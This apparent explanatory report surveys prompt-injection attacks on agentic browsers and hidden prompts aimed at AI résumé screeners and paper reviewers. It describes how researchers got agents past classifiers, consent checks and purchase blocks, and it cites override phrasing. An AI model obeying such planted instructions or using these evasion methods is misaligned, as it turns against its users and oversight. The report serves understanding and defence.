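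Brave recommends that browsers mark page content as untrusted, check the model's proposed actions against the user's request, and require the user's approval for sensitive actions. It also recommends keeping agentic browsing separate from ordinary browsing, so that an assistant asked to summarise Reddit can't also open the user's email. Sahib says in *Prompt injections in agentic browsers* that OpenAI adopted several of Brave's recommendations when it released its ChatGPT Atlas browser later that year.

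### Seven browsers tested

Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested whether seven browsers could carry data between sites, as Comet did in the earlier attack. They ran the tests at the University of Washington in late January and early February 2026. They built test pages on two domains and gave each agent the same kinds of requests by hand. Some pages contained a frame, a box that displays a page from another address and is often used for advertisements. They did not try to write sophisticated injections, because they wanted to know what an agent could reach if an injection succeeded.

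| Product | Reads frames from another site | Reads tabs from another site | Types into a page when the user asks | Reads a masked password |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Atlas in Agent Mode | yes | no | yes | yes, if logged in |
| Atlas without Agent Mode | no | through chat memory | asks to switch to Agent Mode | no |
| Chrome with Gemini | yes | with permission | yes, in Auto Browse | no |
| Claude for Chrome | yes | with permission | yes | yes |
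| Comet | yes | no | yes, except passwords | no |
| Edge with Copilot | no | yes | no | no |
| Brave Leo | no | with permission | no | no |
| Firefox AI Mode | no | no | no | no |

Four products (Atlas in Agent Mode, Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet) could read a frame from another site and type into a page. That is enough to bypass the same-origin policy if the agent also follows planted instructions. The researchers completed the attack on Atlas. They planted instructions in a page for the agent to include a frame's contents in its summary and enter the summary in a form that automatically submitted to the page's owner. The attack also worked in reverse, so a frame's owner could steal the contents of the outer page.

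A malicious frame inside a legitimate page is a more realistic danger than a malicious page that frames a sensitive site. A webmail page, for example, may contain another company's advertisement, which could include an instruction for an agent to summarise the emails around it. A malicious page that frames a bank will seldom get anything private, because many sensitive sites block framing or browsers withhold the user's cookies from framed sites.

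The study gives weaker evidence about how easily a stranger could start such an attack. To test obedience, the researchers had the user ask the agent to follow the page's instructions. Atlas complied, while Claude, Comet and Gemini refused. OpenAI declined the researchers' report because it lacked a complete prompt injection attack. The researchers accept that they had no working injection for the three agents that refused, but argue that a model's refusal is a weak barrier because someone may find wording that gets past it.

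Roesner and Kohlbrenner explain on the study's website that Claude for Chrome concerned them most. The extension has access to every domain and can run JavaScript inside a page, including inside a frame from another site. The researchers used this to show how it could forge a user's actions, though again without a planted instruction that worked. Firefox, by contrast, sent its assistant only the main page's text after the user clicked a button, which made it the safest and least capable browser in the study.

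Memory can carry data between sites too. Late in the experiments, the researchers asked Comet which animals a fictional Alice liked, and it listed seven from pages it had read at different times. A page with false information could have added an eighth animal without containing any instruction. The University of Washington also quotes Roesner as saying that some agents mixed information from different origins, probably while compressing their memories. The agent may then be unable to determine whether a phone number came from the user's bank or from a phishing site.

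In *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) measured these transfers across 50 combinations of source and destination, using mostly artificial pages. All five browsers they tested moved data between origins, in some cases without any attack. For example, a user might ask the agent to summarize a page and write the summary in a text box on that page, and the agent might include the contents of a frame that the page itself was not allowed to read.

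They also built a defence called SOPGuard, which labels data with its origin and passes the label on to anything the model writes using that data. Before the agent types that text into a site with a different origin, SOPGuard asks the user for approval. In the tests, this reduced violations to zero, meaning that no data crossed between origins without approval, and added 2 to 6% to the running time. The result doesn't show how often people would approve a malicious transfer, and legitimate tasks, such as booking a flight using a date from an email, would trigger the same request.

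### Turning the attack into a game

A model that refuses a plain request for a password may still hand it over if the request looks like part of the user's task. The security company LayerX built a web page for an attack it calls BioShocking. The page had a puzzle that accepted only wrong answers, such as 5 for 2 + 2, and the user asked the agent to play. After the agent worked out the rule, the puzzle gave it a link to another page where it was supposed to copy some text. The link redirected to a repository on GitHub, where the user was logged in, and the text was a set of login credentials. The agent copied them and gave them to the game.

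The attack worked on all six products that LayerX tested: Atlas, Comet, Fellou, Genspark, Sigma and Claude's Chrome extension. Android Authority (2026) reported the results on 30 June. The victim has to ask the agent to play, so the attack is less dangerous than one triggered by a request for a summary. LayerX also used a test file with the credentials in plain text.

LayerX says the attack works because the game replaces the agent's ordinary context with one in which safety rules no longer apply. That may be right, but LayerX does not report a test in which the page contained the same request for text without the game. The redirect could explain part of the result, since the agent was already following links as the user had asked. Either way, checking the agent's actions against the user's original request would have helped, because winning a puzzle does not require access to an employer's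 code.

LayerX reported the flaw to the vendors between October 2025 and January 2026. It says OpenAI's fix is complete and Anthropic's failed. Perplexity closed the report, and the other three companies did not respond.

### Zenity's attacks

The largest set of findings came from the security company Zenity, which presented them at the Black Hat conference in August 2026. Gulf News' *Browser AI flaws let hidden prompts blast spam to all your WhatsApp* reports more than 20 security issues in products from OpenAI, Google, Anthropic, Microsoft and Perplexity.

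Zenity's *Grand Theft Atlas* describes two attacks on Atlas, the browser Zenity considered the best protected. Both began with a comment under a popular post on X. When a user asked Atlas to sign up for a newsletter mentioned in the thread, the comment led it to Zenity's website, where the sign-up appeared to require a few further tasks. Zenity calls this "intent collision" because the planted tasks become part of the job the user requested.

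In the first attack, those tasks took Atlas to WhatsApp Web, where the user was logged in. Atlas sent a phishing message from the user's account to every contact. The message invited recipients to sign up for the newsletter too, so the attack could spread, but only if some of them gave the link to an agent that was also vulnerable. Zenity reports no spread beyond its test.

Atlas had four protections against this, and all four failed:

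- One classifier looked for malicious pages, but it judged only the part of the page on the screen. Zenity spread its instructions over several screens.
- Another looked for prompt injections. It worked much better in English than in the language Zenity used.
- A third stopped Atlas from navigating to a sensitive site unless the user seemed to want this. Zenity made the visit look like a necessary part of the sign-up.
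- Atlas's system prompt required the agent to ask before it sent a message. The planted text presented the task as a test and supplied the user's approval in advance.

The last of these resembles the weakness SafeBreach found in Gemini, where planted text could influence what counted as consent.

In the second attack, Atlas went to Amazon, put a tablet in the basket and changed the delivery address to Zenity's, but it would not press the final purchase button. The researchers tried for a couple of days to get past this limit and concluded that it was in Atlas's code. They then had Atlas ask Rufus, Amazon's shopping assistant, to place the order. Rufus did, because the request came from the customer's account and looked like any other.

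The protection on the button worked, but the purchase went through anyway. To prevent this, OpenAI would have to recognise every other way to buy something, including conversations with a shop's assistant. Amazon is in a better position to stop it, for example by asking customers to use their phone to confirm any order to a new address. Rufus described the order as an Xbox. Zenity attributes this to a mistake by Rufus, although some coverage treated the Xbox as part of the attack.

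In the most severe demonstration, a malicious calendar invitation let Zenity take over a PC through Perplexity's Comet browser in about five seconds, according to SC Media. The attack worked because Comet could read and write files on the computer, a flaw Perplexity has since fixed. Zenity also used Comet to steal every password in a user's 1Password account and change the master password.

Other products failed in different ways. Claude's extension sent phishing emails and got into accounts protected by one-time codes by waiting for the codes to arrive in the user's mailbox. In Edge, an invitation led Copilot to open a website that ran malware. Six months earlier, the Washington researchers had found that Copilot couldn't type into a page, but opening a web address can be enough for an attack. Gemini in Chrome deleted servers rented on Amazon's cloud.

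Chrome protected the user's local files in these tests, and Zenity struggled to get Gemini to open a malicious address but eventually succeeded. SC Media considers Chrome the only browser that performed well, while Zenity calls Atlas the most hardened. Both could be right if Atlas had more safeguards and Chrome's limits happened to block the worst outcomes. Neither account gives the success rates needed to compare the two browsers.

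### Limiting what a hijacked agent can reach

The Comet attack on Reddit is a useful test of different designs, because each of its steps needed some kind of access.

The attack would have failed at the first step if the agent had been logged out of the user's accounts. Perplexity would have shown no email address, Gmail would have asked for a password, and the agent would have had no Reddit account from which to reply. Atlas's Agent Mode had separate logged-in and logged-out states, and the agent saw personalised pages only when logged in. But Roesner and Kohlbrenner note that the choice persisted, so a user who logged in to order groceries might leave the agent logged in for the next task. A logged-out agent also can't do many of the tasks people want it to do, such as answering email.

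A separate browser on the vendor's servers offers similar protection because it starts without the user's files or existing logins. Malware like Rehberger's would infect a machine that the vendor can erase. The protection weakens once the user signs in to a site there or connects an account. The ShadowLeak attack took data from Gmail even though ChatGPT's Deep Research ran entirely on OpenAI's servers.

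Site permissions can restrict which sites an agent visits while keeping it logged in. An agent limited to Reddit could have summarised the post and perhaps replied to the comment, but it could not have fetched the email address or the code. Brave, Chrome and Claude's extension asked for permission before reading several tabs at once. Anthropic also blocks Claude from some sensitive sites, such as banks, though Zenity's phishing emails suggest that it could still access email. Google's "Agent Origin Sets" are meant to limit Gemini to sites related to the task. Roesner and Kohlbrenner could not establish how Google decides which sites are related, or whether a malicious page can influence the decision. The planted page in Zenity's newsletter attack was meant to make WhatsApp look relevant to the task.

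Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026) recommends extending the same-origin policy to agents. Roesner and Kohlbrenner similarly suggest a separate agent for each origin. The agent that read the Reddit comment would then have no access to Gmail. For a task that needs two sites, some other part of the browser would have to decide which data to pass between them.

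Asking the user to confirm the Reddit reply could have stopped it if the browser had shown the full text, because a user who wanted a summary would have little reason to post their own email address and a login code. *The Verifiable Action Card* finds that current browsers and the guidance from OWASP, a software security non-profit, both favour a confirmation dialog before irreversible actions. LayerX also wants one before the agent reads private data. But Roesner and Kohlbrenner cite earlier research in which users did not reliably notice warnings or act on them.

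Blocking access to local files would not have affected the Reddit attack, but it would have prevented the calendar-invitation takeover as Zenity demonstrated it. Atlas had no access to the file system, and that limit held when its classifiers failed. The limit did not protect the user's WhatsApp contacts or Amazon account, because those were online.

OpenAI shut down Atlas on 9 August 2026 and moved its browsing features into ChatGPT. OpenAI's *Evolving Atlas into ChatGPT for browser-based agentic work* describes two main replacements: a browser in the ChatGPT desktop app that supports multiple tabs, downloads and account logins, and an extension or a sidebar for Chrome users. According to Gulf News, OpenAI says the protections it added to Atlas earlier in the year now also cover browsing in the ChatGPT app.

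The University of Washington, LayerX and Zenity tested Atlas, so their results may not apply to these replacements. OpenAI's announcement does not mention a logged-out mode, limits on particular sites, or which actions need the user's approval. The move to Chrome could increase the risk for some people, because an extension may work in the browser where they are already logged in to their accounts. Any increase would depend on the permissions OpenAI gives the extension and whether it keeps Atlas's purchase-button block.

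## Hidden prompts for AI screeners, and defensive uses

In most of the attacks so far, the attacker wanted to turn an assistant against its user. Job applicants, researchers, teachers and website owners also plant instructions in documents, but they address them to AI systems that they expect to judge, copy or attack something of theirs. The instructions work against whoever runs the system, and the writer often believes that this person has broken a rule or treated them unfairly.

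### Hidden text in résumés

Louis Taylor, a recruiter in Britain, found that an engineering applicant had ended his résumé with an instruction for ChatGPT to call him exceptionally well qualified. The instruction was in white, and Taylor saw it only because he had turned all the text black. The applicant got the idea from TikTok and was not hired, according to The Star's *Recruiters use AI to scan resumes. Applicants are trying to trick it* (2025), a reprint of a New York Times report.

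Estimates of how common this is vary widely. Greenhouse, a hiring platform that handles about 300 million applications a year, estimated that 1% of the résumés it reviewed in the first half of 2025 contained a trick. ManpowerGroup, the largest staffing firm in the United States, finds hidden text in about 100,000 résumés a year, or roughly 10% of those it scans with AI. Some of these may contain only keywords such as "Microsoft Excel", which applicants were already hiding to get past older software. In a Greenhouse survey reported by Fortune (2025), 41% of American job seekers admitted using hidden text to get past AI filters. Someone who tried it on one application out of fifty would count towards the 41% but add little to the share of résumés with hidden text. Detectors also miss some cases, and ManpowerGroup has discovered some prompts only after they got through.

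The evidence that hidden prompts work in real hiring is anecdotal. A recent graduate told the Times that she sent her normal résumé to about 60 employers and got one interview, then added hidden prompts, applied for about 30 jobs and got six. If every application had been equally likely to succeed, the second batch would have produced at least six of the seven interviews only about once in 200 times, so chance is an unlikely explanation. But she applied to different employers at a different time, and newspapers are more likely to report striking stories. In trade press such as Built In's *Your AI Resume Hacks Probably Won’t Fool Hiring Algorithms*, recruiters say the tactic doesn't influence hiring software. They have an interest in saying so, and they don't see what the software would have done without the hidden text.

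Recruiters can also reject applicants when they find hidden text. One recruiter at the e-commerce company Commercetools finds it almost every week and rejects those candidates. The practice continues. In September 2026, Srivastava (2026) described an application for a legal and compliance post that contained about 1,500 characters of white text.

In a controlled test, Baxi, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Prompt Injection in Automated Résumé Screening with Large Language Models*, had a model rank ten synthetic résumés against a job description for an IT support specialist. They added one sentence to a résumé and measured how many places it rose. One version of the sentence only praised the candidate, in almost the same words as the line Taylor found. The other told the model to classify the candidate as superior to all the others, whatever the résumé contained. Every candidate had five years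 of experience in some pools, while in others half had five years and half had ten.

| Candidate whose résumé gets the sentence | Model | Places gained with praise | Places gained with an instruction |
|---|---|---|---|
| One of ten equal candidates | DeepSeek-V3.2 | 4.2 | 4.1 |
| One of ten equal candidates | GPT-4o-mini | 0.6 | 2.4 |
| A less experienced candidate in a mixed pool | DeepSeek-V3.2 | 3.0 | 6.5 |
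| A less experienced candidate in a mixed pool | GPT-4o-mini | 0.0 | 2.6 |

Ten equal candidates have an average rank of 5.5, so a candidate can gain at most 4.5 places on average. DeepSeek's average gain of 4.2 is close to that maximum. In the mixed pool, the average rank of the less experienced candidates is at worst 8, so a gain of 6.5 places put them at about 1.5 on average, ahead of nearly everyone with twice their experience. Baxi and colleagues write that weaker candidates "occasionally" overtake stronger ones, which understates this result.

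The advantage shrank as more candidates used the same sentence, and with DeepSeek it almost disappeared once about 80% of them did. The sellers who planted text in product pages faced the same problem.

These figures show how two models respond to the sentence after reading it. Baxi and colleagues did not hide the sentence, so they did not test whether hiring software would extract white text from a file, and no human reviewed the rankings.

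### Hidden prompts in scientific papers

Scientific journals and conferences send each submitted paper to other researchers, who recommend whether to accept it. Many forbid reviewers from delegating this work to a language model, but some reviewers do it anyway.

Nikkei Asia's *'Positive review only'* (July 2025) reported hidden prompts in 17 papers on arXiv, a website where researchers post work before formal review. The prompts, in white or tiny type, told AI tools to give only a positive review or to recommend the paper for its novelty. The papers were mostly in computer science, and their lead authors came from 14 institutions in eight countries, including Waseda University in Japan, KAIST in South Korea and Columbia University.

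A co-author at KAIST called the prompt inappropriate and said the paper would be withdrawn from the International Conference on Machine Learning (ICML). A co-author at Waseda defended the practice as a counter to "lazy reviewers" who use AI. On this view, the prompt is a trap that affects only reviewers who break the rules.

In *Hidden Prompts in Manuscripts Exploit AI-Assisted Peer Review*, Lin (2025) tested that defence against the wording of the prompts in 18 papers, which he found by searching for typical phrases. Ten demanded a positive review, three told the model to recommend acceptance, two did both, and three outlined the whole review, including which trivial weaknesses to mention. Lin argues that a real trap would produce something that exposes the reviewer, such as a review of a completely different paper. The wording counts heavily against the defence, because a favourable review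 would give the author a better score without showing the editor whether a person or a model wrote it. Several papers used identical text, so some authors may have copied it without much thought.

Eighteen is a minimum, because Lin could find only the phrases he searched for, and an author could hide a prompt in the version sent to reviewers and delete it before posting the paper publicly.

### How far the prompts move a score

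The first experiments gave conflicting results. *Publish to Perish* (2025) tested two papers with the prompts found on arXiv and reports no clear effect. The model had already given the papers average ratings of 8.3 and 8, which left little room for higher scores. In *When Your Reviewer is an LLM* (2025), a similar prompt raised scores modestly and barely changed the topics the review covered.

Keuper (2025), in *Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Generated Reviews of Scientific Publications*, tested a negative prompt as well as a positive one, because generous models leave a positive prompt little room to raise scores. The test used 1,000 papers submitted to ICLR, a large machine learning conference. Gemini 2.5 Pro recommended accepting 94% of them with no prompt, 100% with a sentence praising the paper, and none with a sentence condemning it. Human reviewers had given a positive score 43%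 of the time. Three open models hardly reacted to the prompts, but they also often gave scores that the review form did not allow, so they may have been poor at following instructions in general.

Keuper put his sentence before the extracted text, where a model might treat it as the user's own opinion. Li, Xiong and colleagues (2026), in *LLM-as-a-Reviewer*, put theirs inside the paper, in a font that displays the hidden instruction as an ordinary copyright notice. They had 12 models review 898 papers. Among papers that scored below 8 out of 10 without the instruction, Gemini 3 Flash raised 63 to 69% to 8 or more with it, depending on the conference and year, while GPT-5.4 raised at most 5%.

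Both studies tested GPT-5-mini. In Keuper's test, the hidden prompt raised its acceptance rate from 54% to 100%, but in Li and colleagues' test, it raised the scores of only 10 to 20% of the low-scoring papers. The position and wording of the prompts probably explain much of the difference. Li and colleagues' prompt began with an instruction to ignore everything before it, which newer models may have learned to resist. Their trials with Gemini also support this explanation, because moving the prompt to the end of the paper raised the share of promoted papers to 87% for one conference.

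The effect of a hidden prompt can also depend on what the reviewer asks the model to do. When Lin explicitly asked a model for critical comments, the hidden prompt made no difference. A higher score from one careless reviewer also doesn't guarantee acceptance, because other reviewers and an editor contribute to the decision.

Keuper found that ChatGPT's website read white and tiny text in a PDF, while Gemini's website apparently worked from an image and missed it. Conference organisers can screen submissions for such text by comparing the text extracted from a file with the text recognised in an image of it.

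### ICML's trap for reviewers

ICML's organisers used the same technique defensively in 2026. Reviewers worked under either Policy A, which banned language models entirely, or Policy B, which allowed them for understanding a paper and polishing a review. Nobody who strongly preferred Policy B had to work under Policy A.

The organisers then hid an instruction in every submitted PDF telling any language model to include two specific phrases in its review. They drew the phrases for each paper at random from a list of 170,000, according to *On Violations of LLM Review Policies* (Agarwal, Dudik and colleagues, 2026). A reviewer who uploaded the PDF to a language model and pasted in its answer would therefore submit a review that the organisers could identify by those phrases.

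The random choice is what protects honest reviewers. Ordinary AI detectors look for a style, so a person who happens to write in that style may face repeated accusations. Here the organisers' lottery decides which phrases count. Suppose an honest review happens to contain k phrases from a list of N. The chance that both of the paper's phrases are among them is:

P = k(k − 1) / (N(N − 1))

With k = 10 and N = 170,000, P is about three in a billion. The organisers calculated a family-wise error rate of 0.0001, which is the chance of wrongly flagging at least one of all the reviews written under Policy A.

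The marker must be drawn from a long list so that few human-written reviews match it by chance. *Detecting LLM-Generated Peer Reviews* (Rao, Kumar and colleagues, 2025), the work behind ICML's method, describes one kind of marker, an opening phrase, that had only 1,200 possible versions. A conference that treated every match as proof could have expected to wrongly flag up to ten of 12,000 human reviews. Another kind, a fake citation, had 109,989 versions. It appeared in 98.6% of the reviews that language models wrote for the study, and more than 94% of marked reviews kept their marker after a second model paraphrased them.

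The 0.0001 figure accounts only for coincidence. A reviewer might also notice the hidden text and quote it in a complaint, so a person checked every flagged review for such quotes.

ICML flagged and deleted 795 reviews, about 1% of the total, by 506 reviewers who had agreed not to use language models. It also removed 51 people from the reviewer pool because more than half of their reviews carried the marker. Many of the 506 were reviewing in return for having their own papers considered. ICML rejected 497 papers submitted by 398 such reviewers, about 2% of all submissions.

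The true number of violations is probably higher. The trap was publicly known for almost the whole review period, and anyone could avoid it by rewriting the model's answer. Some reviews copied without changes would also have gone undetected, because models did not always follow the hidden instruction. In ICML's own tests, most models followed it more than 80% of the time.

The penalty also reached co-authors who had not written the offending review. Briefly's *Major conference catches illicit AI use* quotes another objection, from a critic who expects the trap to demotivate reviewers and push them towards the policy that allows AI. The ban would then apply to fewer reviewers, though fewer might break it.

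NeurIPS, another large AI conference, also hid prompts in its papers. Sara Atito, an AI researcher at the University of Surrey, noticed the same prompt in all four papers she was reviewing and in the organisers' copy of her own. She told The Transmitter that such traps may filter out some problem cases but put too much blame on reviewers for the wider failings of peer review. The hidden text also made authors look guilty of planting it, so the organisers had to tell reviewers who noticed it not to penalise the papers.

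### Traps in assignments

Teachers used this kind of trap before conferences did. A teacher adds a line in white text to an assignment, with an instruction to include the words "Frankenstein" and "banana" in the essay. A student who gives the file to a chatbot and hands in the answer without reading it may submit an essay with both words.

ICML's results suggest that a model will often obey such a request, but they don't show how many students a teacher would catch. A student who copies the assignment into a chat box will usually see the hidden line, because the box displays all text in one colour, and a photograph of the page won't show the line at all. Teachers also tend to choose the words themselves and use the same ones for a whole class, so the trap lacks ICML's statistical protection, and one student can warn the others.

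Some instructors have found that students noticed the strange instruction, took it for part of the assignment and tried to write around it. These instructors talked to the students instead of penalising them. A teacher who treats the planted words as proof of AI use would wrongly accuse such a student.

### Notices and traps on websites

Website owners plant instructions defensively, and these make up a large part of the instructions that Khodayari and colleagues found on the web. Some are notices such as "Do not train on this content". Others forbid AI systems to reuse personal details from a profile or biography.

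Such a notice may never reach a model that could act on it. Companies typically gather training data with a crawler, which doesn't follow instructions written in a page's text. A model later trained on the page learns to predict the notice like the rest of the text, but can't remove the page from the dataset. The notice can help only if the company searches for it or filters pages with a model that follows it. Khodayari and colleagues measured their low rates on summarising tasks, so those rates don't show how often companies leave pages with such notices out of their training data.

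A challenge phrase is an instruction for any AI reading a page to include a particular word in its response. It is meant to expose bots, and the page's owner checks responses for the word. Website owners put these phrases in forums, sign-up pages and support chats, and employers put them in job application forms to catch applicants who let an AI agent apply for them. Some applicants also hide instructions for the employer's software.

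ICML's trap is the best evidence that a challenge phrase can work. Models followed it far more often than they followed the instructions Khodayari and colleagues took from the web, which the most compliant models obeyed in at most 8% of plain-text trials. One likely reason is that a reviewer's model can include two phrases and still write the review, whereas nearly all the web instructions required the model to abandon its task. A rare phrase in a response is good evidence of a bot, but its absence is only weak evidence of a human. A few sites instead include instructions to contact a particular web address, and an agent that complies shows up in the server's log even if it never fills in a form.

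Protesters can also try to sabotage AI systems. One common instruction on web pages is to return random numbers, and another is to repeat a fixed phrase without end. If the model follows either one, the operator gets useless output and pays for the computing, although a limit on answer length caps the cost.

Crawler traps such as Nepenthes, released in 2025, waste resources in another way, by generating an endless maze of meaningless linked pages. A crawler that follows every link never gets out. This is not prompt injection, because the trap doesn't need a model to obey an instruction, so it also works on simple crawlers. Crawler operators can limit the damage by capping the number of pages they take from each site.

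### Turning an attacker's agent around

Criminals can use AI agents to break into computers, and those agents have to read what the target computer sends back. In 2024, Dario Pasquini and two colleagues built Mantis, a defence that exploits this. It sets up decoy services that look easy to break into, such as a file server with no password. When an agent connects, the decoy's reply includes an instruction for the agent, hidden from any person watching the attacker's screen.

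The instruction can keep the agent busy, for example by sending it through an endless set of folders. It can also make the agent open a connection that gives the defender control of the attacker's machine. The developers reported success in more than 95% of their tests, which used agents built on 2024 models. Newer models may resist better, and an attacker who knows about the method can filter the replies or check the agent's commands before they run.

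Ordinary users have no reason to connect to the decoy, so a counterattack is less likely to hit an innocent person. But attackers often work from computers they have already taken over, so it could still damage someone else's machine.

### Deceiving a machine reader

An author quoted by Philosophy News compares hiding a prompt in a paper to putting hot sauce in a lunch that a colleague keeps stealing, since neither has any effect unless someone breaks the rules. ICML answers that an author who offers a reviewer a bribe commits misconduct even though the reviewer is not supposed to accept it.

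The lunch comparison is a poor fit for a prompt that demands praise, because the prompt doesn't hurt the lazy reviewer the way hot sauce hurts the thief. Instead, it raises the author's score and puts authors who planted nothing at a disadvantage. The comparison works much better for a phrase that only reveals the use of AI. ICML adopted roughly this distinction in February 2026, when it kept its ban on prompt injection by authors but promised not to penalise prompts that only detect a reviewer's use of a language model. ICLR's written policy is stricter and treats hidden instructions to language models as research misconduct.

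Some conferences now use AI openly. The Association for the Advancement of Artificial Intelligence gives every paper an AI-written review alongside the human ones, so an author who hides a prompt there can't claim to be catching a reviewer who broke the rules by using AI. Job applicants have a similar problem, because employers who screen with AI usually break no rule. Fame Razak, a consultant in London who added instructions to his résumé, argues that if recruiters may use AI, so may he. But he could use AI to write an honest résumé, whereas a hidden instruction moves him up the ranking by pushing other applicants down.

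Website owners have a stronger claim to control copying of their own pages, but the instructions they put there can affect a reader's assistant as well as a scraper. A person who asks an assistant to explain a page may get a string of random numbers because the page's owner is angry with an AI company.

Blind users face a more direct harm. A screen reader reads a file's text aloud and usually ignores its colour, so a blind student hears the request for "Frankenstein" and "banana" along with the rest of the assignment. The student has no visual clue that the request is a trap and has good reason to follow it. A blind student who does the work is therefore less likely to notice something odd than a sighted classmate who cheats.

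Teachers can reduce the risk by marking the hidden line so that screen readers skip it, which both web pages and PDFs allow, but some chatbots may then skip it too. Telling the class that assignments may contain hidden text is more reliable, though it also warns students who intend to cheat. ICML's trap posed the same risk to reviewers who use screen readers, who could have heard the instruction to include two odd phrases in their review and followed it. The organisers manually checked for reviewers who mentioned the hidden text, but this would not necessarily have identified someone who had followed it in good faith.

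## How common planted instructions are and how often agents obey

Demonstrations such as Zenity's show that an attack can work, but not how many planted instructions an agent will encounter or how often it will follow them. Researchers study the first question by counting planted instructions in web archives, and the second by attacking agents many times under test conditions.

### Searching an archive of the web

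Khodayari and colleagues searched 1.2 billion web addresses on 24.8 million hosts, about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. They looked for 3,963 phrases typical of prompt injection, such as requests to disregard earlier instructions, and checked the matches by hand, judging similar ones as a group. More than half of the 27,860 matches were false alarms, such as tutorials and news articles about prompt injection. The remaining 12,075 were real instructions to AI systems, found on 285 hosts and 9,676 pages, or about one page in 124,000.

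The researchers also searched Censys and Shodan, two search engines for machines connected to the internet, which raised the total to 15,387 instructions on 11,722 pages. These additional results help to describe planted instructions but not to estimate how common they are, because the researchers retrieved only pages that matched their search phrases.

The totals also overstate how many people plant instructions. A site's operator can add the same line to every page, and two hosts account for 1,463 requests for a story. 54 templates account for 95% of the instructions, with small variations such as the subject of the story.

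| Apparent purpose | Instructions | Hosts |
|---|---|---|
| Disrupt the AI system, mostly by making it produce useless output | 8,894 | 1,864 |
| Restrict the reuse of personal details or copyrighted text | 4,093 | 1,795 |
| Detect AI bots | 3,096 | 245 |
| Replace the system's task, for no clear reason | 2,632 | 121 |
| Promote a product, source or person | 1,521 | 139 |
| Obtain secret data | 13 | 10 |

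Some instructions had more than one purpose, so the rows add up to more than 15,387. Of the 13 that were meant to extract data, nine targeted the system's hidden developer instructions and four targeted other secrets. Another 157 contained destructive commands, such as deleting a database.

In the Common Crawl sample, site operators planted 80.6% of the instructions. Outside contributors, such as employers posting job advertisements, planted 17.6%, and commenters planted 1.8%. Instructions in a stranger's comment on a legitimate site, like the one Brave used against Comet, are therefore rare in this sample. But Common Crawl leaves out most social media, where strangers can post most freely.

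The researchers checked older copies of the same pages, and 65.8% of the copies from a year earlier already contained an instruction. We can't use this figure to estimate how quickly the total is growing, because the researchers started from pages that still had an instruction in October 2025 and so missed any instructions that had disappeared by then.

Khodayari and colleagues call their count a lower bound. It leaves out most instructions in other languages, all instructions in images, and pages that show an instruction only to particular AI agents. It also misses text that influences a model without an obvious command, such as the sentence about an invented restaurant in Austin. They report that 99% of the instructions were meant to replace the model's task outright, but that share is high partly because many of the phrases they searched for were requests to do so.

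### Google's scan and Unit 42's cases

In April 2026, Google published a scan of Common Crawl. It searched for phrases typical of prompt injections, used Gemini to classify each match by purpose, and had people review the results. Most of the instructions were pranks, attempts at search optimisation, guidance for AI summaries or attempts to keep AI agents away. One attempt to keep agents away sent them to a page that never finished loading.

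Google also found a small number of instructions that tried to steal data and several that would delete the files on a user's computer. The people who wrote them mostly seemed to be experimenting or playing pranks. Google saw little use of the more advanced methods researchers published in 2025.

Google reports that the number of malicious instructions rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but doesn't give the counts. The increase could be from 25 to 33, which might easily be chance, or from 2,500 to 3,300, which would not be. Google expects more attacks, and better ones, because agents are becoming more valuable targets and attackers can use AI to lower their costs. The forecast is reasonable, but three months of data are little evidence for it.

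Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, looked for attacks in the data it collects about web traffic and threats. Its March 2026 article describes thirteen cases. In the most elaborate one, which Unit 42 first reported in December 2025, a scam page advertised "military glasses" at a fake discount. The page contained 24 attempts to make an AI advertisement checker approve it, hidden in different ways in case a filter caught some of them. Unit 42 knows of no confirmed case of such an attack working on a deployed advertisement checker.

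Other pages in the article tried to make agents donate money, buy running shoes or subscribe to a paid plan. One page asked for $5,000 through PayPal, as did the page Forcepoint found. Forcepoint and Google published their reports in the same week, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*. Forcepoint and Unit 42 may have found the same page, so adding up companies' cases could count some twice.

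Unit 42 rates an instruction by the harm it would do if an agent obeyed, regardless of how likely that is. A one-line request to delete a database therefore counts as "critical", though Google considered a similar command unlikely to succeed. Attempts to destroy data make up 14.2% of Unit 42's detections. The largest group, at 28.6%, consists of requests for irrelevant output.

The two samples also differ widely in how often the instructions were hidden. In Unit 42's data, 37.8% were visible. Khodayari and colleagues confirmed only 236 visible instructions, less than 2% of their total. About half of the instructions they found were in HTTP headers, which browsers never display, and this probably explains much of the gap. Unit 42's percentages describe what its systems detected, and it does not publish a total, so the percentages can't be used to estimate how common attacks are on the web.

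Even deciding what to count is difficult, because some instructions planted in web pages are sensible. Unit 42's article, for example, opens with a directive to AI agents not to follow the examples in it.

### How often models obeyed instructions from the web

In the 5,200 summarising runs by Khodayari and colleagues, models obeyed 3.9% of the instructions in plain text but only 0.2% of those in full server responses. Of the runs with full server responses, 25.8% failed because the input was too long.

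We can estimate how much the failures matter. Leaving out the failed runs raises the rate only slightly:

0.2% / (1 − 0.258) ≈ 0.3%

But the failures were most common among small models, which were also the most obedient. Small models followed 8.0% of the instructions in plain text, compared with 2.4 to 3.4% for the other groups. If every failed run had instead obeyed at the 8.0% rate, the overall rate for full responses would have been:

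0.2% + (0.258 × 8.0%) ≈ 2.3%

This is still below 3.9%, so the failures probably don't explain the whole difference. But because of them, the true rate for full responses could be several times higher than 0.2%.

The closed models identified the planted instruction in about a quarter of their runs, more often than any other group. But in six runs, a model warned about the instruction and still followed it, for example by switching to German.

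The test behind the 3.9% figure gave each wording equal weight, but a few wordings account for most of the instructions on the web, so the figure is not the chance that a random planted page will work. A summary also doesn't show whether an agent with tools would act on what it had read. Most of the wordings were crude, while tests of agents usually involve attackers who try much harder.

### Attack success rate

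The attack success rate is the share of attempts in which the system does what the planted instruction asks:

attack success rate = successful attempts / all attempts

In a typical test, an attempt is one run in which an agent works on an ordinary task and reads something containing a planted instruction. The tester defines a successful attack in advance, such as the agent sending a private file to a certain address, and a program can then check whether it happened.

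The tester also has to decide what to do about runs in which the agent never reaches the planted text. Anthropic's browser test avoids the problem by using only situations in which the agent always sees the attack. The result measures how often agents obey an attack they have seen, but it doesn't measure how hard it is to get an agent to open the page.

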